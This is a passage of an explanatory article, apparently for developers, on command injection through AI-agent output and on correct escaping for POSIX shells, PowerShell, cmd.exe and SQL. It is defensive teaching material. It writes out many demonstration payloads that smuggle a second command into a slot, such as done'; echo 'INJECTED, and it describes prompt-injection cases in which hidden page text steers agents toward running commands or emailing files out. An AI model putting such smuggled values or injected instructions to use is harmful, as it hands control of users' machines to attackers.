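# Sanitising and sandboxing the output of AI agents: escaping, stripping and command injection

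## How an agent's output becomes a command

An AI agent is a language model that acts by calling tools, such as running commands or editing files. The model produces only text, which other software turns into actions. Sometimes this software parses text meant as data as part of a command, which changes what runs. Security engineers call this command injection, and they knew it as a flaw of web forms and databases long before language models existed. Agents have made it newly common because so much of what they write goes straight into programs that execute text as commands. Developers can sanitise the text, which means changing it before use to make it safe, or run the resulting command in a sandbox, where it can reach little of value, and most carefully built systems do some of both.

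### Agents, harnesses and interpreters

The harness is the ordinary program around the model. *Agentic Large Language Models* (2026) defines an agent as a language model plus a harness, which builds prompts, processes answers, calls external tools and repeats the cycle until the task is complete. *Natural-Language Agent Harnesses* (2026) adds that the harness determines what input the model receives, which tools it may call and when execution may stop. Anthropic's glossary makes the same distinction for its coding product: "Claude Code is the harness; Claude is the model inside it".

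An interpreter is any program that parses text and acts on it. A shell, the program behind a command line, splits a line of text into a program name and its arguments and starts the program. A database engine does something similar with SQL queries, and a browser with the HTML and JavaScript of a web page. A terminal window is also an interpreter, because it acts on control codes in the text it displays. Each interpreter has its own set of special characters, and the same character can have different meanings in different interpreters. For example, an opening angle bracket starts a tag in a web page but redirects input from a file in a shell. A semicolon separates commands in a shell but is ordinary punctuation in the body of a web page.

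### From the model to the running program

"The model never runs anything on its own," according to Anthropic's *How tool use works*. The developer describes the available tools and their inputs, and the harness sends these descriptions to the model with the user's request. To call a tool, the model includes in its reply a structured block with the tool's name and its arguments in JSON, a plain-text format for labelled values. The harness extracts the arguments, performs the operation and sends back the result. The model then either requests another tool or finishes. OpenAI's *Function calling* describes the same arrangement, in which the model passes data and the application's code takes the action.

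Suppose a user asks for a list of the Python files in a folder. In the example in Anthropic's *Bash tool*, the model responds with a request for the tool named `bash` and a field that contains `ls *.py`. The command is only text in a JSON field and has no effect until the harness copies it into a running shell. The shell replaces `*.py` with the names of the matching files and runs the program `ls`, which prints them. The harness then returns the output to the model.

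The JSON wrapper guarantees only that there is a field called `command` with a string in it, not what the string contains. In Claude Code, that string can be any command the user could run, according to Anthropic's *How Claude Code works*.

Agents also write text outside tool calls, such as summaries, file names, descriptions of code changes and a closing message to the user. Harnesses use this text too, often in places where nobody thinks of it as a command.

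### The notification example

Agents work for long stretches, and people wander off. In a forum thread titled *Feature request: notifications when codex is done with a task*, users of OpenAI's coding agent Codex trade ways of getting an alert on the desktop or the phone. Suppose a harness on Linux does this by pasting the agent's one-line status message into a shell command:

```
notify-send 'Agent' 'MESSAGE'
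```

The program `notify-send` shows a desktop notification with a title and a text. The developer fixed everything in the line except `MESSAGE`, which marks a slot, the place in a command template where outside text goes in as data. The single quotation marks around it instruct the shell to treat everything between them as one literal piece of text. "All tests passed" works, and so do hundreds of other messages. Then one day the agent reports that the build didn't finish:

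```
notify-send 'Agent' 'the build didn't finish'
```

In a shell, an apostrophe and a closing single quotation mark are the same character, so the quotation ends after `didn`. The letters `t finish` fall outside it, and the last mark opens a new quotation that never closes. The shell reports a syntax error and the user gets no notification.

Nobody attacked anything there. But consider the message `done'; echo 'INJECTED`, which produces this line:

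```
notify-send 'Agent' 'done'; echo 'INJECTED'
```

The quotation marks now balance, so the shell runs the first command up to the semicolon and then the second, which prints the word INJECTED. An attacker could replace this harmless command with any other. The part of a malicious text that is meant to run is called the payload. The user sees a normal notification that reads "done". Both messages trigger the same defect, so a harness that fails on "didn't" should get a security review as well as a bug report.

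OpenAI's Codex CLI, the terminal version of Codex, briefly contained almost exactly this code. An April 2025 change, *feat: add notifications for MacOS using Applescript*, took the agent's last message, replaced line breaks with spaces, cut the text to 100 characters and put a backslash before every double quotation mark. It then inserted the result, in a variable named `safePreview`, into a shell command that ran a line of AppleScript, the automation language of macOS. The shell command enclosed the AppleScript in single quotation marks, but the code didn't escape apostrophes, so an apostrophe in the message could end the quoted text and let the shell run what followed as a command. The contributor mentioned having "yolo'ed it with codex", so the agent had apparently helped write this vulnerable code in its own harness.

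Bolin (2025) repaired the flaw within days in *use spawn instead of exec to avoid injection vulnerability (#416)*, and pointed out that the name of the current folder went into the same command and could also carry a payload. His patch started the AppleScript program directly, without a shell, but AppleScript still interpreted the message. He added that he was unsure of AppleScript's escaping rules, so the text might still do harm there. A year later, Gen Agent Trust Hub's *notify* (2026), an audit of a notification add-on for agents, reported the same AppleScript weakness and rated the add-on high risk.

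### Why the output is untrusted when the user is honest

An agent's status messages may carry an attack even though users have no reason to attack their own laptops, because the agent reads things the user did not write. Web pages, emails and code from strangers reach the model as text alongside the user's request, and some of that text may contain instructions. Prompt injection occurs when the model follows those instructions.

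David C explains why language models are vulnerable to prompt injection in *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a 2025 article for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre. A database engine handles instructions and stored data differently, so developers can keep the two separate. A language model predicts the next token (a word or piece of a word) from all the text so far, with no built-in boundary between the developer's words and a stranger's. In his example, a recruitment system uses a model to score CVs, and a candidate hides an instruction to approve the CV in its text. He thinks it quite possible that no one will ever eliminate prompt injection the way developers can eliminate SQL injection.

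Text can reach an agent without being visible to a human reader. Howard (2026), in *The Attack That Arrived as a Footnote*, describes a test in which Claude and Codex prepared answer sheets for an algebra quiz. One version of the PDF included a sixth problem that readers could not see but software could extract, and both assistants solved it. This is only mild evidence that they were deceived, since a helpful assistant might well answer an extra problem anyway. Saxton (2026), in *Hidden prompts in web content*, tested his own system with a fake council page about bin collections that hid six instructions, including one to run a command and one to email his configuration files to an outside address. His text extractor dropped two and passed the other four to the model as ordinary page text, though a model that receives such instructions will not necessarily follow them. Mascellino (2026),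 in *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents*, reports that the security company Zscaler found websites with hidden text meant to manipulate agents into making cryptocurrency payments.

In the public competition behind *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (2026), 464 participants attempted 272,000 such attacks against 13 leading models, and 8,648 succeeded, about 3 percent. Every model was vulnerable, with success rates ranging from 0.5 percent for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5 percent for Gemini 2.5 Pro. Later models do better. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports Anthropic's figures for Claude Opus 5, which show no successful attacks in 129 browser scenarios and a 2.0 percent success rate after 15 attempts on a more general test, compared with 5.5 percent for its predecessor, Opus 4.8. These figures can't be compared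 directly with the competition's because the two count success differently. A 2 percent success rate is still a concern for harness authors, because an attacker can easily put the same text in front of a great many agents.

A flaw in Claude Desktop, Anthropic's desktop application, allowed prompt injection to lead to command injection. Koi Security's *PromptJacking* describes extensions that placed their input into AppleScript commands without escaping it. eSecurity Planet's *PromptJacking* reproduces one template, which told the Chrome browser to open a web address and had a slot for that address. If the model fetched a hostile page to answer a user's innocent question, the page could steer the model into filling the slot with text that ended the quotation and started a shell command. Infosecurity Magazine's *Claude Desktop Extensions Vulnerable to Web-Based Prompt Injection* names three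 affected official extensions and gives a severity of 8.9 out of 10 on the standard CVSS scale. Correct escaping would have prevented this attack even if the model were fully under the page's influence.

An agent can also make plain mistakes, such as getting its quoting wrong. *What makes a harness a harness* (2026) warns that language models under pressure tend to give whatever answer seems to satisfy the request, true or not. It calls polite instructions to the model the weakest of controls and recommends that ordinary code verify the real state of things instead.

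### Improper output handling

OWASP, a foundation that publishes widely used lists of software security risks, includes this problem in its top ten for language-model applications. *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling* defines the weakness as insufficient validation, sanitisation and handling of a model's output before it passes to other components and systems. According to the entry, whoever influences the prompt can influence the output, so an application that forwards the output unexamined gives that person indirect access to the systems behind the application. The entry distinguishes this from overreliance, the broader worry that people trust a model's answers too much.

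The consequences depend on which interpreter receives the text. In browsers, OWASP lists cross-site scripting, where an attacker's script runs inside a page the victim trusts, and cross-site request forgery, where the victim's browser sends a request the victim never intended. On servers, it lists server-side request forgery (the server makes requests the attacker chooses), privilege escalation and remote code execution. Its examples include output that goes directly into a shell, database queries that run without protection, and file paths built from model text, which can lead outside the intended folder.

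The entry's first piece of advice is to "treat the model as any other user". This is exactly right for the notification, and web developers have decades of practice at distrusting what users type into forms. The advice is only partly sufficient for a coding agent, because much of the agent's job is to run shell commands, which few websites invite their users to type.

### A slot or a whole command

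In the notification, the developer wrote the command and the agent supplies the message as a value. For every possible message, the correct outcome is that the user sees its characters on the screen. The developer can design the harness for this outcome without making it interpret the message.

With the Bash tool, the agent's output is the command. In `ls *.py`, the asterisk has to keep its special meaning for the command to list the Python files. If the harness escaped the whole string as literal data, the shell would look for a program named `ls *.py` and fail to find one. The harness has no template to protect here and has to determine whether the command is acceptable, which is much harder to code.

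In one OWASP scenario, a user asks a database chatbot for a query that deletes every table, and the model writes one. In another, a coding model invents the name of a software package, and a developer who installs it may download malware. Both the query and the install command can be valid syntax, so escaping has nothing to correct. The OWASP entry does not distinguish these cases from those where the model only fills a slot in a fixed command. It recommends parameterised queries, which send values to the database separately from the SQL text, for all database operations that involve model output. These protect a fixed query that takes a customer's name from the model, but they don't help when the model writes the entire query.

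The two can also nest. An agent that writes a command to record a code change may copy the description from a stranger's bug report. It has then created a slot and must quote the text correctly itself.

Four kinds of defence apply to these cases. Escaping rewrites text so that a specific interpreter reads it as the same literal data. Stripping deletes or replaces characters or patterns thought to be dangerous. Checking accepts or rejects text without changing it. Sandboxing runs code in an environment where the operating system or a virtual machine limits what the code can reach. In the notification example, escaping would display "didn't" intact, while stripping the apostrophe would display "didnt". A check might reject the whole message, and a sandbox would let `echo INJECTED` run but limit the damage it could do.

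## What correct escaping guarantees

An escaping function is correct if the interpreter always reads the escaped text back as the original text and nothing more. To put this precisely, let T be a command template with one slot, and write T[x] for the text that results when the harness puts x into the slot. An escaping function e is correct for that template and a given interpreter if, for every string s,

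```
parse(T[e(s)]) = C(s)
```

Here `parse` is the interpreter's reading of a text, and C(s) is the command the developer intended, containing one literal whose value is s. A literal is a value written directly in a command, such as a number or a quoted string. In the notification example, C(s) is "run `notify-send` with the title Agent and the text s", and only s varies.

The equation requires that s leave the command's structure unchanged and arrive unaltered. A function that replaced every message with "ok" would meet the first requirement but not the second. The equation must also hold for every string, because an attacker needs only one string for which it fails. Tests can find mistakes, but they cover only some strings, so establishing correctness requires a proof from the interpreter's grammar.

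### Two definitions of injection

Buro and Mastroeni note in *Abstract Code Injection* that few of the many studies on code injection attacks try to define the attack itself. In *The Essence of Command Injection Attacks in Web Applications* (2006), Su and Wassermann gave what they describe as the first formal definition. It uses the parse tree, a diagram of a command's grammar with the whole command at the root and single words and symbols at the leaves. Each piece of outside text must make up exactly the leaves below one node of the tree, and the developer must allow that kind of node. If the command parses but some input fails this test, the command is an injection attack.

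The paper's main example is an online shop that looks up a customer's stored credit cards with a database query ending in `uname='John' AND cardtype=2`. The customer supplies both the name and the card type, and the developer has escaped both by doubling every apostrophe, which is how SQL represents an apostrophe inside a quoted string. But the card type is a number with no quotation marks around it, so a customer can send `2 OR 1=1`, which contains no apostrophe to escape. The condition is then true for every row, and the shop returns every card number in the database. In the parse tree, the `2` belongs to the comparison with `cardtype` while `OR 1=1` attaches higher up, so no single node covers exactly the input.

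By this definition, the message that printed INJECTED was an attack, but the agent's message about the build that "didn't finish" was not, because the resulting command did not parse.

Su and Wassermann implemented their definition in a program called SQLCHECK. It puts markers around each input, lets the application assemble its query, and then parses the query with a modified grammar that allows markers only around a complete node of a permitted kind. They proved that it blocks every attack under their definition and no other valid query. They tested it on five web applications, each written in two programming languages. In each language it blocked all 18,424 attack requests and allowed all 3,824 legitimate ones, adding about 3 milliseconds per query. However, nobody had designed these attacks to defeat SQLCHECK, and Su and Wassermann acknowledge that an attacker could search for the four-letter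 strings it used as markers.

In *Defining Code-injection Attacks* (2012), Ray and Ligatti argued that the parse tree is the wrong basis for detecting injection. If an application expects a PIN and an attacker sends `exit()`, SQLCHECK can accept the input because a function call is a complete node, yet the attacker has made the database run a function. The input `1000>GLOBAL` is also a complete node, and an attacker can work out the value of a hidden variable by repeating it with different numbers. SQLCHECK makes the opposite error when an application joins a file name `f` and an extension `e` into the string `'f.e'`. It reports an attack because neither input fills a node on its own, although both are plain data.

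Ray and Ligatti propose that an injection occurs when any character of untrusted input ends up outside a closed value. A closed value is a piece of data with nothing left to compute and no variables to fill in, such as `5` or `'John'`. Their definition agrees with SQLCHECK's on only three of the eleven example queries they compare.

That count is slightly unfair to Su and Wassermann, who let developers choose which kinds of node to allow. A policy that permitted only literals would reject both `exit()` and `1000>GLOBAL`. Ray and Ligatti reply that developers have no clear way to know which kinds to allow, and that the same kind can be data in one place and code in another. The number 40 is data in a comparison, but in `CHAR(40)` it sets the type of a database column. No choice of policy helps with `'f.e'`. Ray and Ligatti's definition is the better general one, but the dispute hardly matters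 for a harness that fills one slot with one message, because a correctly escaped message forms one complete literal, which is both a permitted node and a closed value.

Ray and Ligatti also proved that escaping, or something equivalent, is necessary. They showed that, in a simplified version of SQL, any application that always copies some untrusted input unchanged into its query is open to injection if at least one non-empty input yields a valid query. They did so by constructing the attack. For a string, the attacker closes the quotation, adds a variable and opens a new quotation, so that `'fname'` becomes `'f' + GLOBAL + 'name'`. For a number, the attacker needs no quotation mark, and `-100` can become `-1 * exit() * 2100`. The theorem does not apply to an application that escapes its input, because escaping changes some strings.

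### A proof for the POSIX shell

POSIX is the standard that defines how Unix-like systems, including their shells, behave. Under POSIX, every character between single quotation marks is literal, and a single quotation mark cannot occur between them (The Open Group, 2024). Putting a backslash before one does not help, according to GNU's manual for Bash, the most common Linux shell.

Python's standard library has a function for this shell, `shlex.quote`. It belongs to a module that Raymond (1998) originally wrote, and the current source code has three cases. An empty string becomes `''`. A string made up only of unaccented letters, digits, underscores and the characters `% + , - . / : = @` stays as it is. For any other string, the function replaces each apostrophe with the five characters `'"'"'` and puts single quotation marks around the result. The word "didn't" becomes:

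```
'didn'"'"'t'
```

The function supplies its own quotation marks, so the developer has to remove those in the notification template and write `notify-send 'Agent' MESSAGE`. Leaving them in would be worse than not escaping at all for some messages. The text `done; echo INJECTED` is harmless between the original quotation marks, but with a second pair it produces this line:

```
notify-send 'Agent' ''done; echo INJECTED''
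```

The shell reads two empty quotations with a live command between them, and prints INJECTED.

The proof that the function is correct begins with the strings that it puts in quotation marks. Let s be such a string, with no null byte (a byte with the value zero) in it. Cut s at its apostrophes into pieces p₀, p₁, …, pₙ, some of which may be empty. None of the pieces contains an apostrophe, and the output is:

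```
'p₀'"'"'p₁'"'"' … '"'"'pₙ'
```

The shell reads this from left to right. The opening single quotation mark starts a string in which every character is literal, and since p₀ contains no apostrophe, the string ends exactly where the function closed it. A double quotation mark then starts a string containing only an apostrophe. The shell takes this apostrophe literally, because only the dollar sign, the backquote and the backslash keep a special meaning between double quotation marks. The double-quoted string then closes, a single-quoted string opens for p₁, and the same steps repeat up to pₙ.

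Every character of s is therefore inside some quotation, so none can act as a command separator, a word separator or the start of a substitution. The pieces also form a single word, because under The Open Group's rules for splitting a line into words, the end of a quotation does not end the word, and the output has nothing unquoted between quotations. After the shell removes the enclosing quotation marks, that word is p₀'p₁'…'pₙ, which is s.

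The function turns an empty string into `''`, which the shell reads as an empty word. It leaves some other strings unquoted, and the Open Group lists four of the characters they may contain, `%`, `,`, `-` and `=`, as special in some circumstances. An equals sign can assign a variable if the word comes before the command name. The other three matter only inside constructs that also need a character such as `$` or `{`, and the function quotes any string containing one of those. Words like `if` are also special only in certain positions, chiefly at the start of a command. If the slot is a separate word among the arguments of an ordinary command, as in the notification template, the shell takes all these strings literally, which completes the proof. Developers can avoid having to consider the unquoted strings by using the function's newer option `force=True`, which puts every string in quotation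 marks.

The proof excludes null bytes because Unix programs treat them as the end of a string, so no quoting can make it possible to pass one in an argument. Docs.rs' *Module shlex::quoting_warning*, the documentation of a similar library for Rust, shows that Bash sometimes drops a null byte and sometimes cuts the text off there. A harness should reject strings that contain null bytes.

### The conditions the proof uses

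The proof holds only under five conditions, and a harness can violate any of them while calling a flawless escaping function.

- The developer knows which interpreter will read the text. The documentation for Python's *shlex* warns that the function is only for Unix shells and that its output may allow command injection on Windows.
- The developer knows where in the template the text will go. With the template `echo MESSAGE>log.txt`, the message "2" stays unquoted and the shell reads `2>` as an instruction to redirect error messages. In the shop's query, the escaping was right for a quoted string and the slot held a number.
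- The escaping function and the interpreter use the same character encoding, so that they agree on which bytes form which characters. Docs.rs describes a case in Bash on macOS, where the single byte A0, which is invalid in the usual UTF-8 encoding, can separate two words. Versions of the Rust library before 1.3.0 did not quote it.
- Exactly one interpreter parses the text, and it does so once.
- Nothing changes the text after escaping. If a harness shortens an escaped message to 100 characters, it may cut off the closing quotation mark, and the shell then treats the rest of the template as part of the message. OpenAI's notification code for Codex got this right, at least, because it shortened the message first.

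Correct escaping can fail in a live terminal session because an interactive shell has a line editor that handles keystrokes before the shell parses anything. The byte for Ctrl-A moves the cursor to the start of the line, even inside quotation marks. If a harness types a correctly quoted message that contains this byte followed by `echo INJECTED;`, the editor inserts those words in front of the intended command, and the shell runs them. RustSec, which publishes security advisories for Rust software, calls this risk "essentially unfixable" for the Rust library, though control characters are safe in a non-interactive shell. The 2024 edition of POSIX includes a quoting form, `$'…'`, that can represent control characters as codes, but the library does not use it because some common shells, such as Dash, do not support it.

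### When a second interpreter parses the text

Each parse removes one layer of quoting. Suppose the notification should appear on another computer, which the harness reaches with `ssh`, the usual program for running commands remotely. The harness escapes the message once:

```
ssh home notify-send Agent 'done; echo INJECTED'
```

The local shell behaves exactly as the proof predicts. It removes the quotation marks and passes `done; echo INJECTED` to `ssh` as a single argument. But `ssh` then joins its arguments with spaces, according to the manual from OpenBSD, and sends the result to the other computer. It has to send a single string, as Stuge (2023), in *command [argument ...] in ssh(1)*, points out, because the protocol has room for only one, and the server hands that string to the user's shell. The remote shell receives this:

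```
notify-send Agent done; echo INJECTED
```

It shows "done" and then prints INJECTED.

The same behaviour also causes errors when there is no attack. Watson (2020), in *Why are the arguments supplied for the command run through ssh interpreted*, gives the example of `ssh host cat 'path with spaces'`, which the remote shell splits into four words, so `cat` looks for three files. The Wooledge wiki's *ssh eats my word boundaries!* demonstrates the problem with a small program that counts its arguments. The program reports two arguments when run locally and three when run through `ssh`.

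The remedy is to escape once for each parse, starting with the interpreter that reads the text last. The harness escapes the message, builds the complete remote command, and then escapes that whole command for the local shell:

```
ssh home 'notify-send Agent '"'"'done; echo INJECTED'"'"''
```

This is hard to read and easy to get wrong by hand, but two calls to `shlex.quote` produce it reliably if both shells follow POSIX.

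A shell inside a shell can fail from the other direction. Suppose the template is `sh -c "notify-send Agent MESSAGE"`, which starts a second shell to run the command between the double quotation marks. The developer escapes the message for the inner shell only, and the message is `$(echo INJECTED)`, which is shell notation for "run this command and insert its output here":

```
sh -c "notify-send Agent '$(echo INJECTED)'"
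```

The outer shell treats the single quotation marks as ordinary characters because they are inside double quotation marks, where the dollar sign keeps its special meaning. It therefore runs `echo INJECTED` before the inner shell starts, and the user gets a notification that reads "INJECTED".

Adding extra layers of escaping for safety does not work either, because the surplus marks become part of the value. The old protocol of `scp`, the file-copying program in OpenSSH (the most widely used version of `ssh`), passed file names through the remote shell, so users had to quote special characters twice or risk running part of a file name as a command. OpenSSH's *release 9.0* (2022) switched `scp` by default to a protocol that does not pass file names through the remote shell, and warned that the old "finicky and brittle quoting" could now make transfers fail.

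The second parse may also come much later. When a database receives an escaped value, it correctly stores the original text without the escaping. If another program later copies that text into a command without escaping it again, the payload runs. Su and Wassermann cite these attacks, known as second-order attacks, as a reason escaping quotation marks can fail.

### What escaping leaves undecided

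Escaping preserves a value without checking whether it is harmful or false. The strings `../private.txt`, `http://localhost/admin` and `--help` contain only characters that are safe for the shell, so `shlex.quote` returns all three unchanged. But a program that opens the path may leave its intended folder, and one that fetches the address may reach a service meant only for the local machine. `notify-send` will read `--help` as an option and print its instructions. This is a small case of argument injection, in which a value remains one argument but the program treats it as an option. Ray and Ligatti give a database example in which the value `TRUE` replaces a password. It is a closed value and injects no code, but it may cause a type error that the application doesn't expect. A false report that all tests passed will also reach the user unchanged.

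Escaping also has no role when the agent writes the whole command, since there is no C(s) to preserve. The formal definitions don't help much here. Under Ray and Ligatti's definition, nearly every command from the Bash tool is an injection. They accept this and cite phpMyAdmin, a web tool in which users type their own database commands, as a case where programmers expect injections and don't consider them malicious. Under Su and Wassermann's definition, the result depends on the policy, since a whole command is always a complete node. A policy that allows commands accepts everything the agent writes, and a policy that allows only literals rejects both `ls *.py` and a command to delete the folder.

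## Escaping rules for shells, databases, web pages and terminals

A harness needs to format the agent's status message differently for almost every destination. The apostrophe in "didn't" can break a shell command or a database query, but it is harmless in the text of a web page, where a `<` can cause problems.

### POSIX shells

A shell command has three positions for the message, each with its own correct form:

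```
notify-send Agent the\ build\ didn\'t\ finish
notify-send Agent 'the build didn'"'"'t finish'
notify-send Agent "the build didn't finish"
```

All three lines show the same notification. In the first, nothing encloses the text, so each special character needs its own backslash. The Open Group lists fifteen characters that always need protection, including the space, and fourteen more that need it in some circumstances, and warns that a future standard may widen those circumstances. A backslash can't protect one of the fifteen, the line break, because the shell reads a backslash before a line break as a sign that the command continues on the next line, and deletes both. Backslashes alone therefore can't correctly escape messages that may span several lines.

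Inside single quotation marks, only the apostrophe has to be replaced, using the five-character sequence from the POSIX proof. Inside double quotation marks, the apostrophe is an ordinary character, but the dollar sign, backquote, backslash and double quotation mark each need a backslash in front. For example, the message `$(echo INJECTED)` becomes `"\$(echo INJECTED)"`. A function that doesn't escape the backslash itself is unsafe, because it turns `\"` into `\\"`, which the shell reads as a literal backslash followed by the end of the string. In an interactive Bash session, an exclamation mark inside double quotation marks can also recall an earlier command. A backslash prevents this but remains in the message.

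Developers mostly want double quotation marks because the template contains a variable, as in `"$USER: MESSAGE"`. They can close the quotation marks before `MESSAGE`, as in `"$USER: "MESSAGE`, and replace `MESSAGE` with the output of `shlex.quote`. The shell joins adjacent quoted strings into one word.

For longer texts there is also the here-document, which feeds the lines that follow a command to that command as input:

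```
cat <<'END'
the build didn't finish
END
```

The quotation marks around the first `END` make the shell read every line literally until it reaches a line consisting only of `END`. Nothing in the text needs escaping, but there is no way to escape a line of the message that consists only of `END`, so the harness has to choose an end marker that does not occur in the text.

### PowerShell

PowerShell is Microsoft's newer command shell. Microsoft's *about_Quoting_Rules* distinguishes verbatim strings, in single quotation marks, from expandable strings, in double ones. PowerShell passes on a verbatim string exactly as typed, except that two apostrophes in a row stand for one. In an expandable string it replaces `$name` with the value of that variable, and runs any expression inside `$(…)` and inserts the result. With a script called `notify.ps1` in place of `notify-send`, the message looks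 like this in each kind:

```
./notify.ps1 'the build didn''t finish'
./notify.ps1 "the build didn't finish"
```

If a notification's message is in a PowerShell verbatim string, the text `$(echo INJECTED)` appears unchanged. In an expandable string, PowerShell runs it and the notification reads "INJECTED". An expandable string therefore needs a backtick, PowerShell's escape character, before every dollar sign, double quotation mark and backtick in the message. A verbatim string is simpler for outside text.

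Microsoft supplies a function for escaping verbatim strings in PowerShell, `EscapeSingleQuotedStringContent`. Microsoft's *CodeGeneration.EscapeSingleQuotedStringContent(String) Method* shows the developer adding the enclosing quotation marks by hand, whereas `shlex.quote` adds them automatically. A developer who moves a harness from Linux to Windows and swaps one function for the other has to add quotation marks to the template, or the message will have none around it. The function is safer than a homemade replacement because PowerShell accepts several kinds of quotation mark as delimiters.

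Microsoft's *Preventing script injection attacks* treats this function as a fallback. Its example is a script that looks up a running process by its number. The script pastes the number into a string and hands the string to `Invoke-Expression`, a command that parses and runs whatever text it receives. If the "number" is a real process number followed by a semicolon and a command to print a word, the script finds the process and then prints the word. The guide works through four repairs:

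- Declaring the parameter as an integer makes PowerShell reject the text before it reaches the string.
- Calling the lookup command directly, without `Invoke-Expression`, leaves nothing to parse the semicolon. The lookup command receives the whole text as a process number and rejects it.
- Single quotation marks around the slot stop this payload, but not one that contains an apostrophe.
- The escaping function inside those quotation marks stops both.

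The guide recommends avoiding `Invoke-Expression` and escaping only when it can't be avoided. The first repair doesn't help with a status message, because any text is legitimate. The guide also recommends Injection Hunter, a module by Lee Holmes that searches PowerShell scripts for risky patterns of this kind.

### Windows command lines and cmd.exe

A Unix program receives its arguments as separate strings. Windows gives each new process a single string, and the program has to split it. According to Microsoft's *Everyone quotes command line arguments the wrong way*, a post from 2011, most programs follow one convention for this. Double quotation marks enclose an argument that contains spaces, and a backslash marks a double quotation mark that belongs to the value. The message `test "login" failed` becomes:

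```
"test \"login\" failed"
```

Backslashes are ordinary characters unless they come right before a quotation mark, in which case each must be doubled. People often forget this with folder names. In `"C:\my files\"` the last backslash makes the closing quotation mark part of the name, and the argument continues into the next one.

The older Windows shell, cmd.exe, does not follow this convention. The post describes it as a text preprocessor, which transforms a whole line and leaves the splitting into arguments to the program it starts. To cmd.exe a double quotation mark switches quoting on or off, and a backslash in front changes nothing. Take the message `done"&echo INJECTED`, correctly escaped for an ordinary Windows program:

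```
notify.exe "done\"&echo INJECTED"
```

If the harness starts `notify.exe` directly, the program receives the message intact. If the line goes through cmd.exe, quoting ends at the second quotation mark, so the ampersand separates two commands and the shell prints INJECTED followed by a stray quotation mark.

Quotation marks don't protect a percent sign in cmd.exe. The shell replaces `%USERNAME%` with the user's name even inside a quoted string, because it expands variables before it looks at quotation marks. A variable whose value contains a quotation mark can therefore end a quotation. A POSIX shell, by contrast, keeps the result of an expansion between double quotation marks literal. *how does the windows command interpreter cmd exe parse scripts*, a question-and-answer page, uses experiments to divide cmd.exe's parsing into phases, with percent signs handled first and quotation marks,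 carets and ampersands in the next phase. The page presents this as a model that predicts how scripts behave but may not match the program's internals.

For historical reasons, cmd.exe expands environment variables when it reads a line, before it runs any command on that line. Microsoft's *Environment variable expansion occurs when the command is read* (2006) gives the example of a variable `VAR` that holds the word "before". The line `set VAR=after & echo %VAR%` prints "before", because cmd.exe fills in the old value before it runs `set`. Early versions of the shell, written in assembly language, used a simple loop that read a line, expanded the variables and evaluated the result. Later versions kept this as the default so that existing scripts would still work, and added an optional form called delayed expansion, which uses exclamation marks and expands variables when the command runs.

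The escape character in cmd.exe is the caret. The 2011 post advised developers to escape each argument by the usual convention and then put a caret before every character special to cmd.exe, including quotation marks. For an ordinary program this handles the ampersand, but it doesn't reliably stop variable expansion, because cmd.exe expands variables before it processes carets. It is also not enough for batch files, the `.bat` and `.cmd` scripts that cmd.exe itself runs. When a batch file uses its arguments, cmd.exe inserts them into the file's lines and parses those lines again, after it has removed the carets.

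### BatBadBut

Many languages let a program start another with an argument list, in which the program name and arguments are separate strings and no shell parses them. On Windows, the language's runtime library has to join the list into one string, and runtimes escaped the arguments with backslashes, following the usual convention. *BatBadBut* (RyotaK, April 2024) described what happened when the program was a batch file. Windows cannot run a batch file on its own, so its process-creation function, `CreateProcess`, silently starts cmd.exe. The arguments therefore reached a shell even though the developer had asked for none, and they had been escaped for a different interpreter.

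The name is a pun on batch files and "bad, but not the worst". The flaw affects programs that run a batch file with an argument an attacker can influence. Running an `.exe` file does not trigger it. Developers can run a batch file without noticing, because some runtimes respond to a request for `test` by running `test.bat` if they find one. On Windows, the JavaScript package manager npm, which coding agents run often, starts from a batch file called `npm.cmd`.

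RyotaK recorded that Haskell, Node.js, PHP and Rust got patches for the problem, while Erlang, Go, Python and Ruby got documentation changes and Java's maintainers declined to fix it. CERT/CC, which coordinates the disclosure of software flaws, pointed out that Microsoft had documented some of the escaping problems as early as 2011.

Rust's case was awkward because its documentation promised that arguments would reach the new process unchanged and that no shell would evaluate them. In *CVE-2024-24576*, Albini (2024) rated the flaw critical for anyone who passed untrusted arguments to batch files, and said that no other use was affected. Rust already had separate escaping rules for batch files, but they were not thorough enough, and its developers improved them without finding a solution that was correct in all cases. Since version 1.77.2, Rust has therefore returned an `InvalidInput` error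 when it cannot escape an argument safely. The equation for correct escaping then holds for every string that Rust accepts, but some notifications never appear, so a harness has to handle the error, perhaps by showing a fixed message instead.

RyotaK did publish a recipe for runtimes without a fix. The developer turns off the runtime's own escaping, doubles any backslash before a quotation mark, doubles the quotation marks and encloses the whole in another pair. Each percent sign becomes `%%cd:~,%`, whose second part expands to nothing and keeps the first percent sign from starting a variable. The message `100% "done"` turns into this:

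```
"100%%cd:~,% ""done"""
```

The recipe depends on cmd.exe having delayed expansion off and command extensions on. It also deletes line breaks, so it fails the requirement that the text arrive unaltered. RyotaK found in tests that it prevented injection, but he was not sure it was the best method.

Rust's first repair did not recognise every batch file. It applied the cmd.exe escaping rules only if the program's name ended in `.bat` or `.cmd`. Windows ignores spaces and full stops at the end of a file name, so it runs `notify.cmd.` as `notify.cmd`, but Rust did not treat that name as a batch file and applied the wrong rules. The flaw was in this check, not in the cmd.exe escaping rules. Albini (2024), in *Security advisory for the standard library (CVE-2024-43402)*, rated its severity as low because few programs would meet the conditions. Rust 1.81.0, released in September 2024, fixed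 it.

The languages have since adopted different policies. Node.js' *Child process* documentation for version 26 states that `execFile`, which normally starts a program without a shell, cannot launch batch files. The other ways to launch them all use cmd.exe, and Node.js advises against one of these, the `shell` option. Python still adds no escaping when Windows starts a shell for a batch file. Its documentation suggests considering `shell=True` when deliberately launching a batch file with untrusted arguments, so that Python can escape special characters. This is nearly the opposite of the advice for Node.js.

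Python's `shlex.quote` does not make text safe for cmd.exe, because it encloses the text in apostrophes, which cmd.exe treats as ordinary characters. A 2020 bug report, *subprocess docs don't qualify the instruction to use shlex.quote by OS*, gives an example in which the output of `shlex.quote` starts a second program. Rust documentation added in *Auto merge of #123681* recommends restricting untrusted arguments to batch files as much as possible. To send a notification, the harness can avoid the problem by calling a program by its full name, such as `notify.exe`, and never calling a batch file.

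### SQL

Suppose the harness also logs each message in a database, along with the number of failed tests:

```
INSERT INTO log (message, failures) VALUES ('the build didn''t finish', 3)
```

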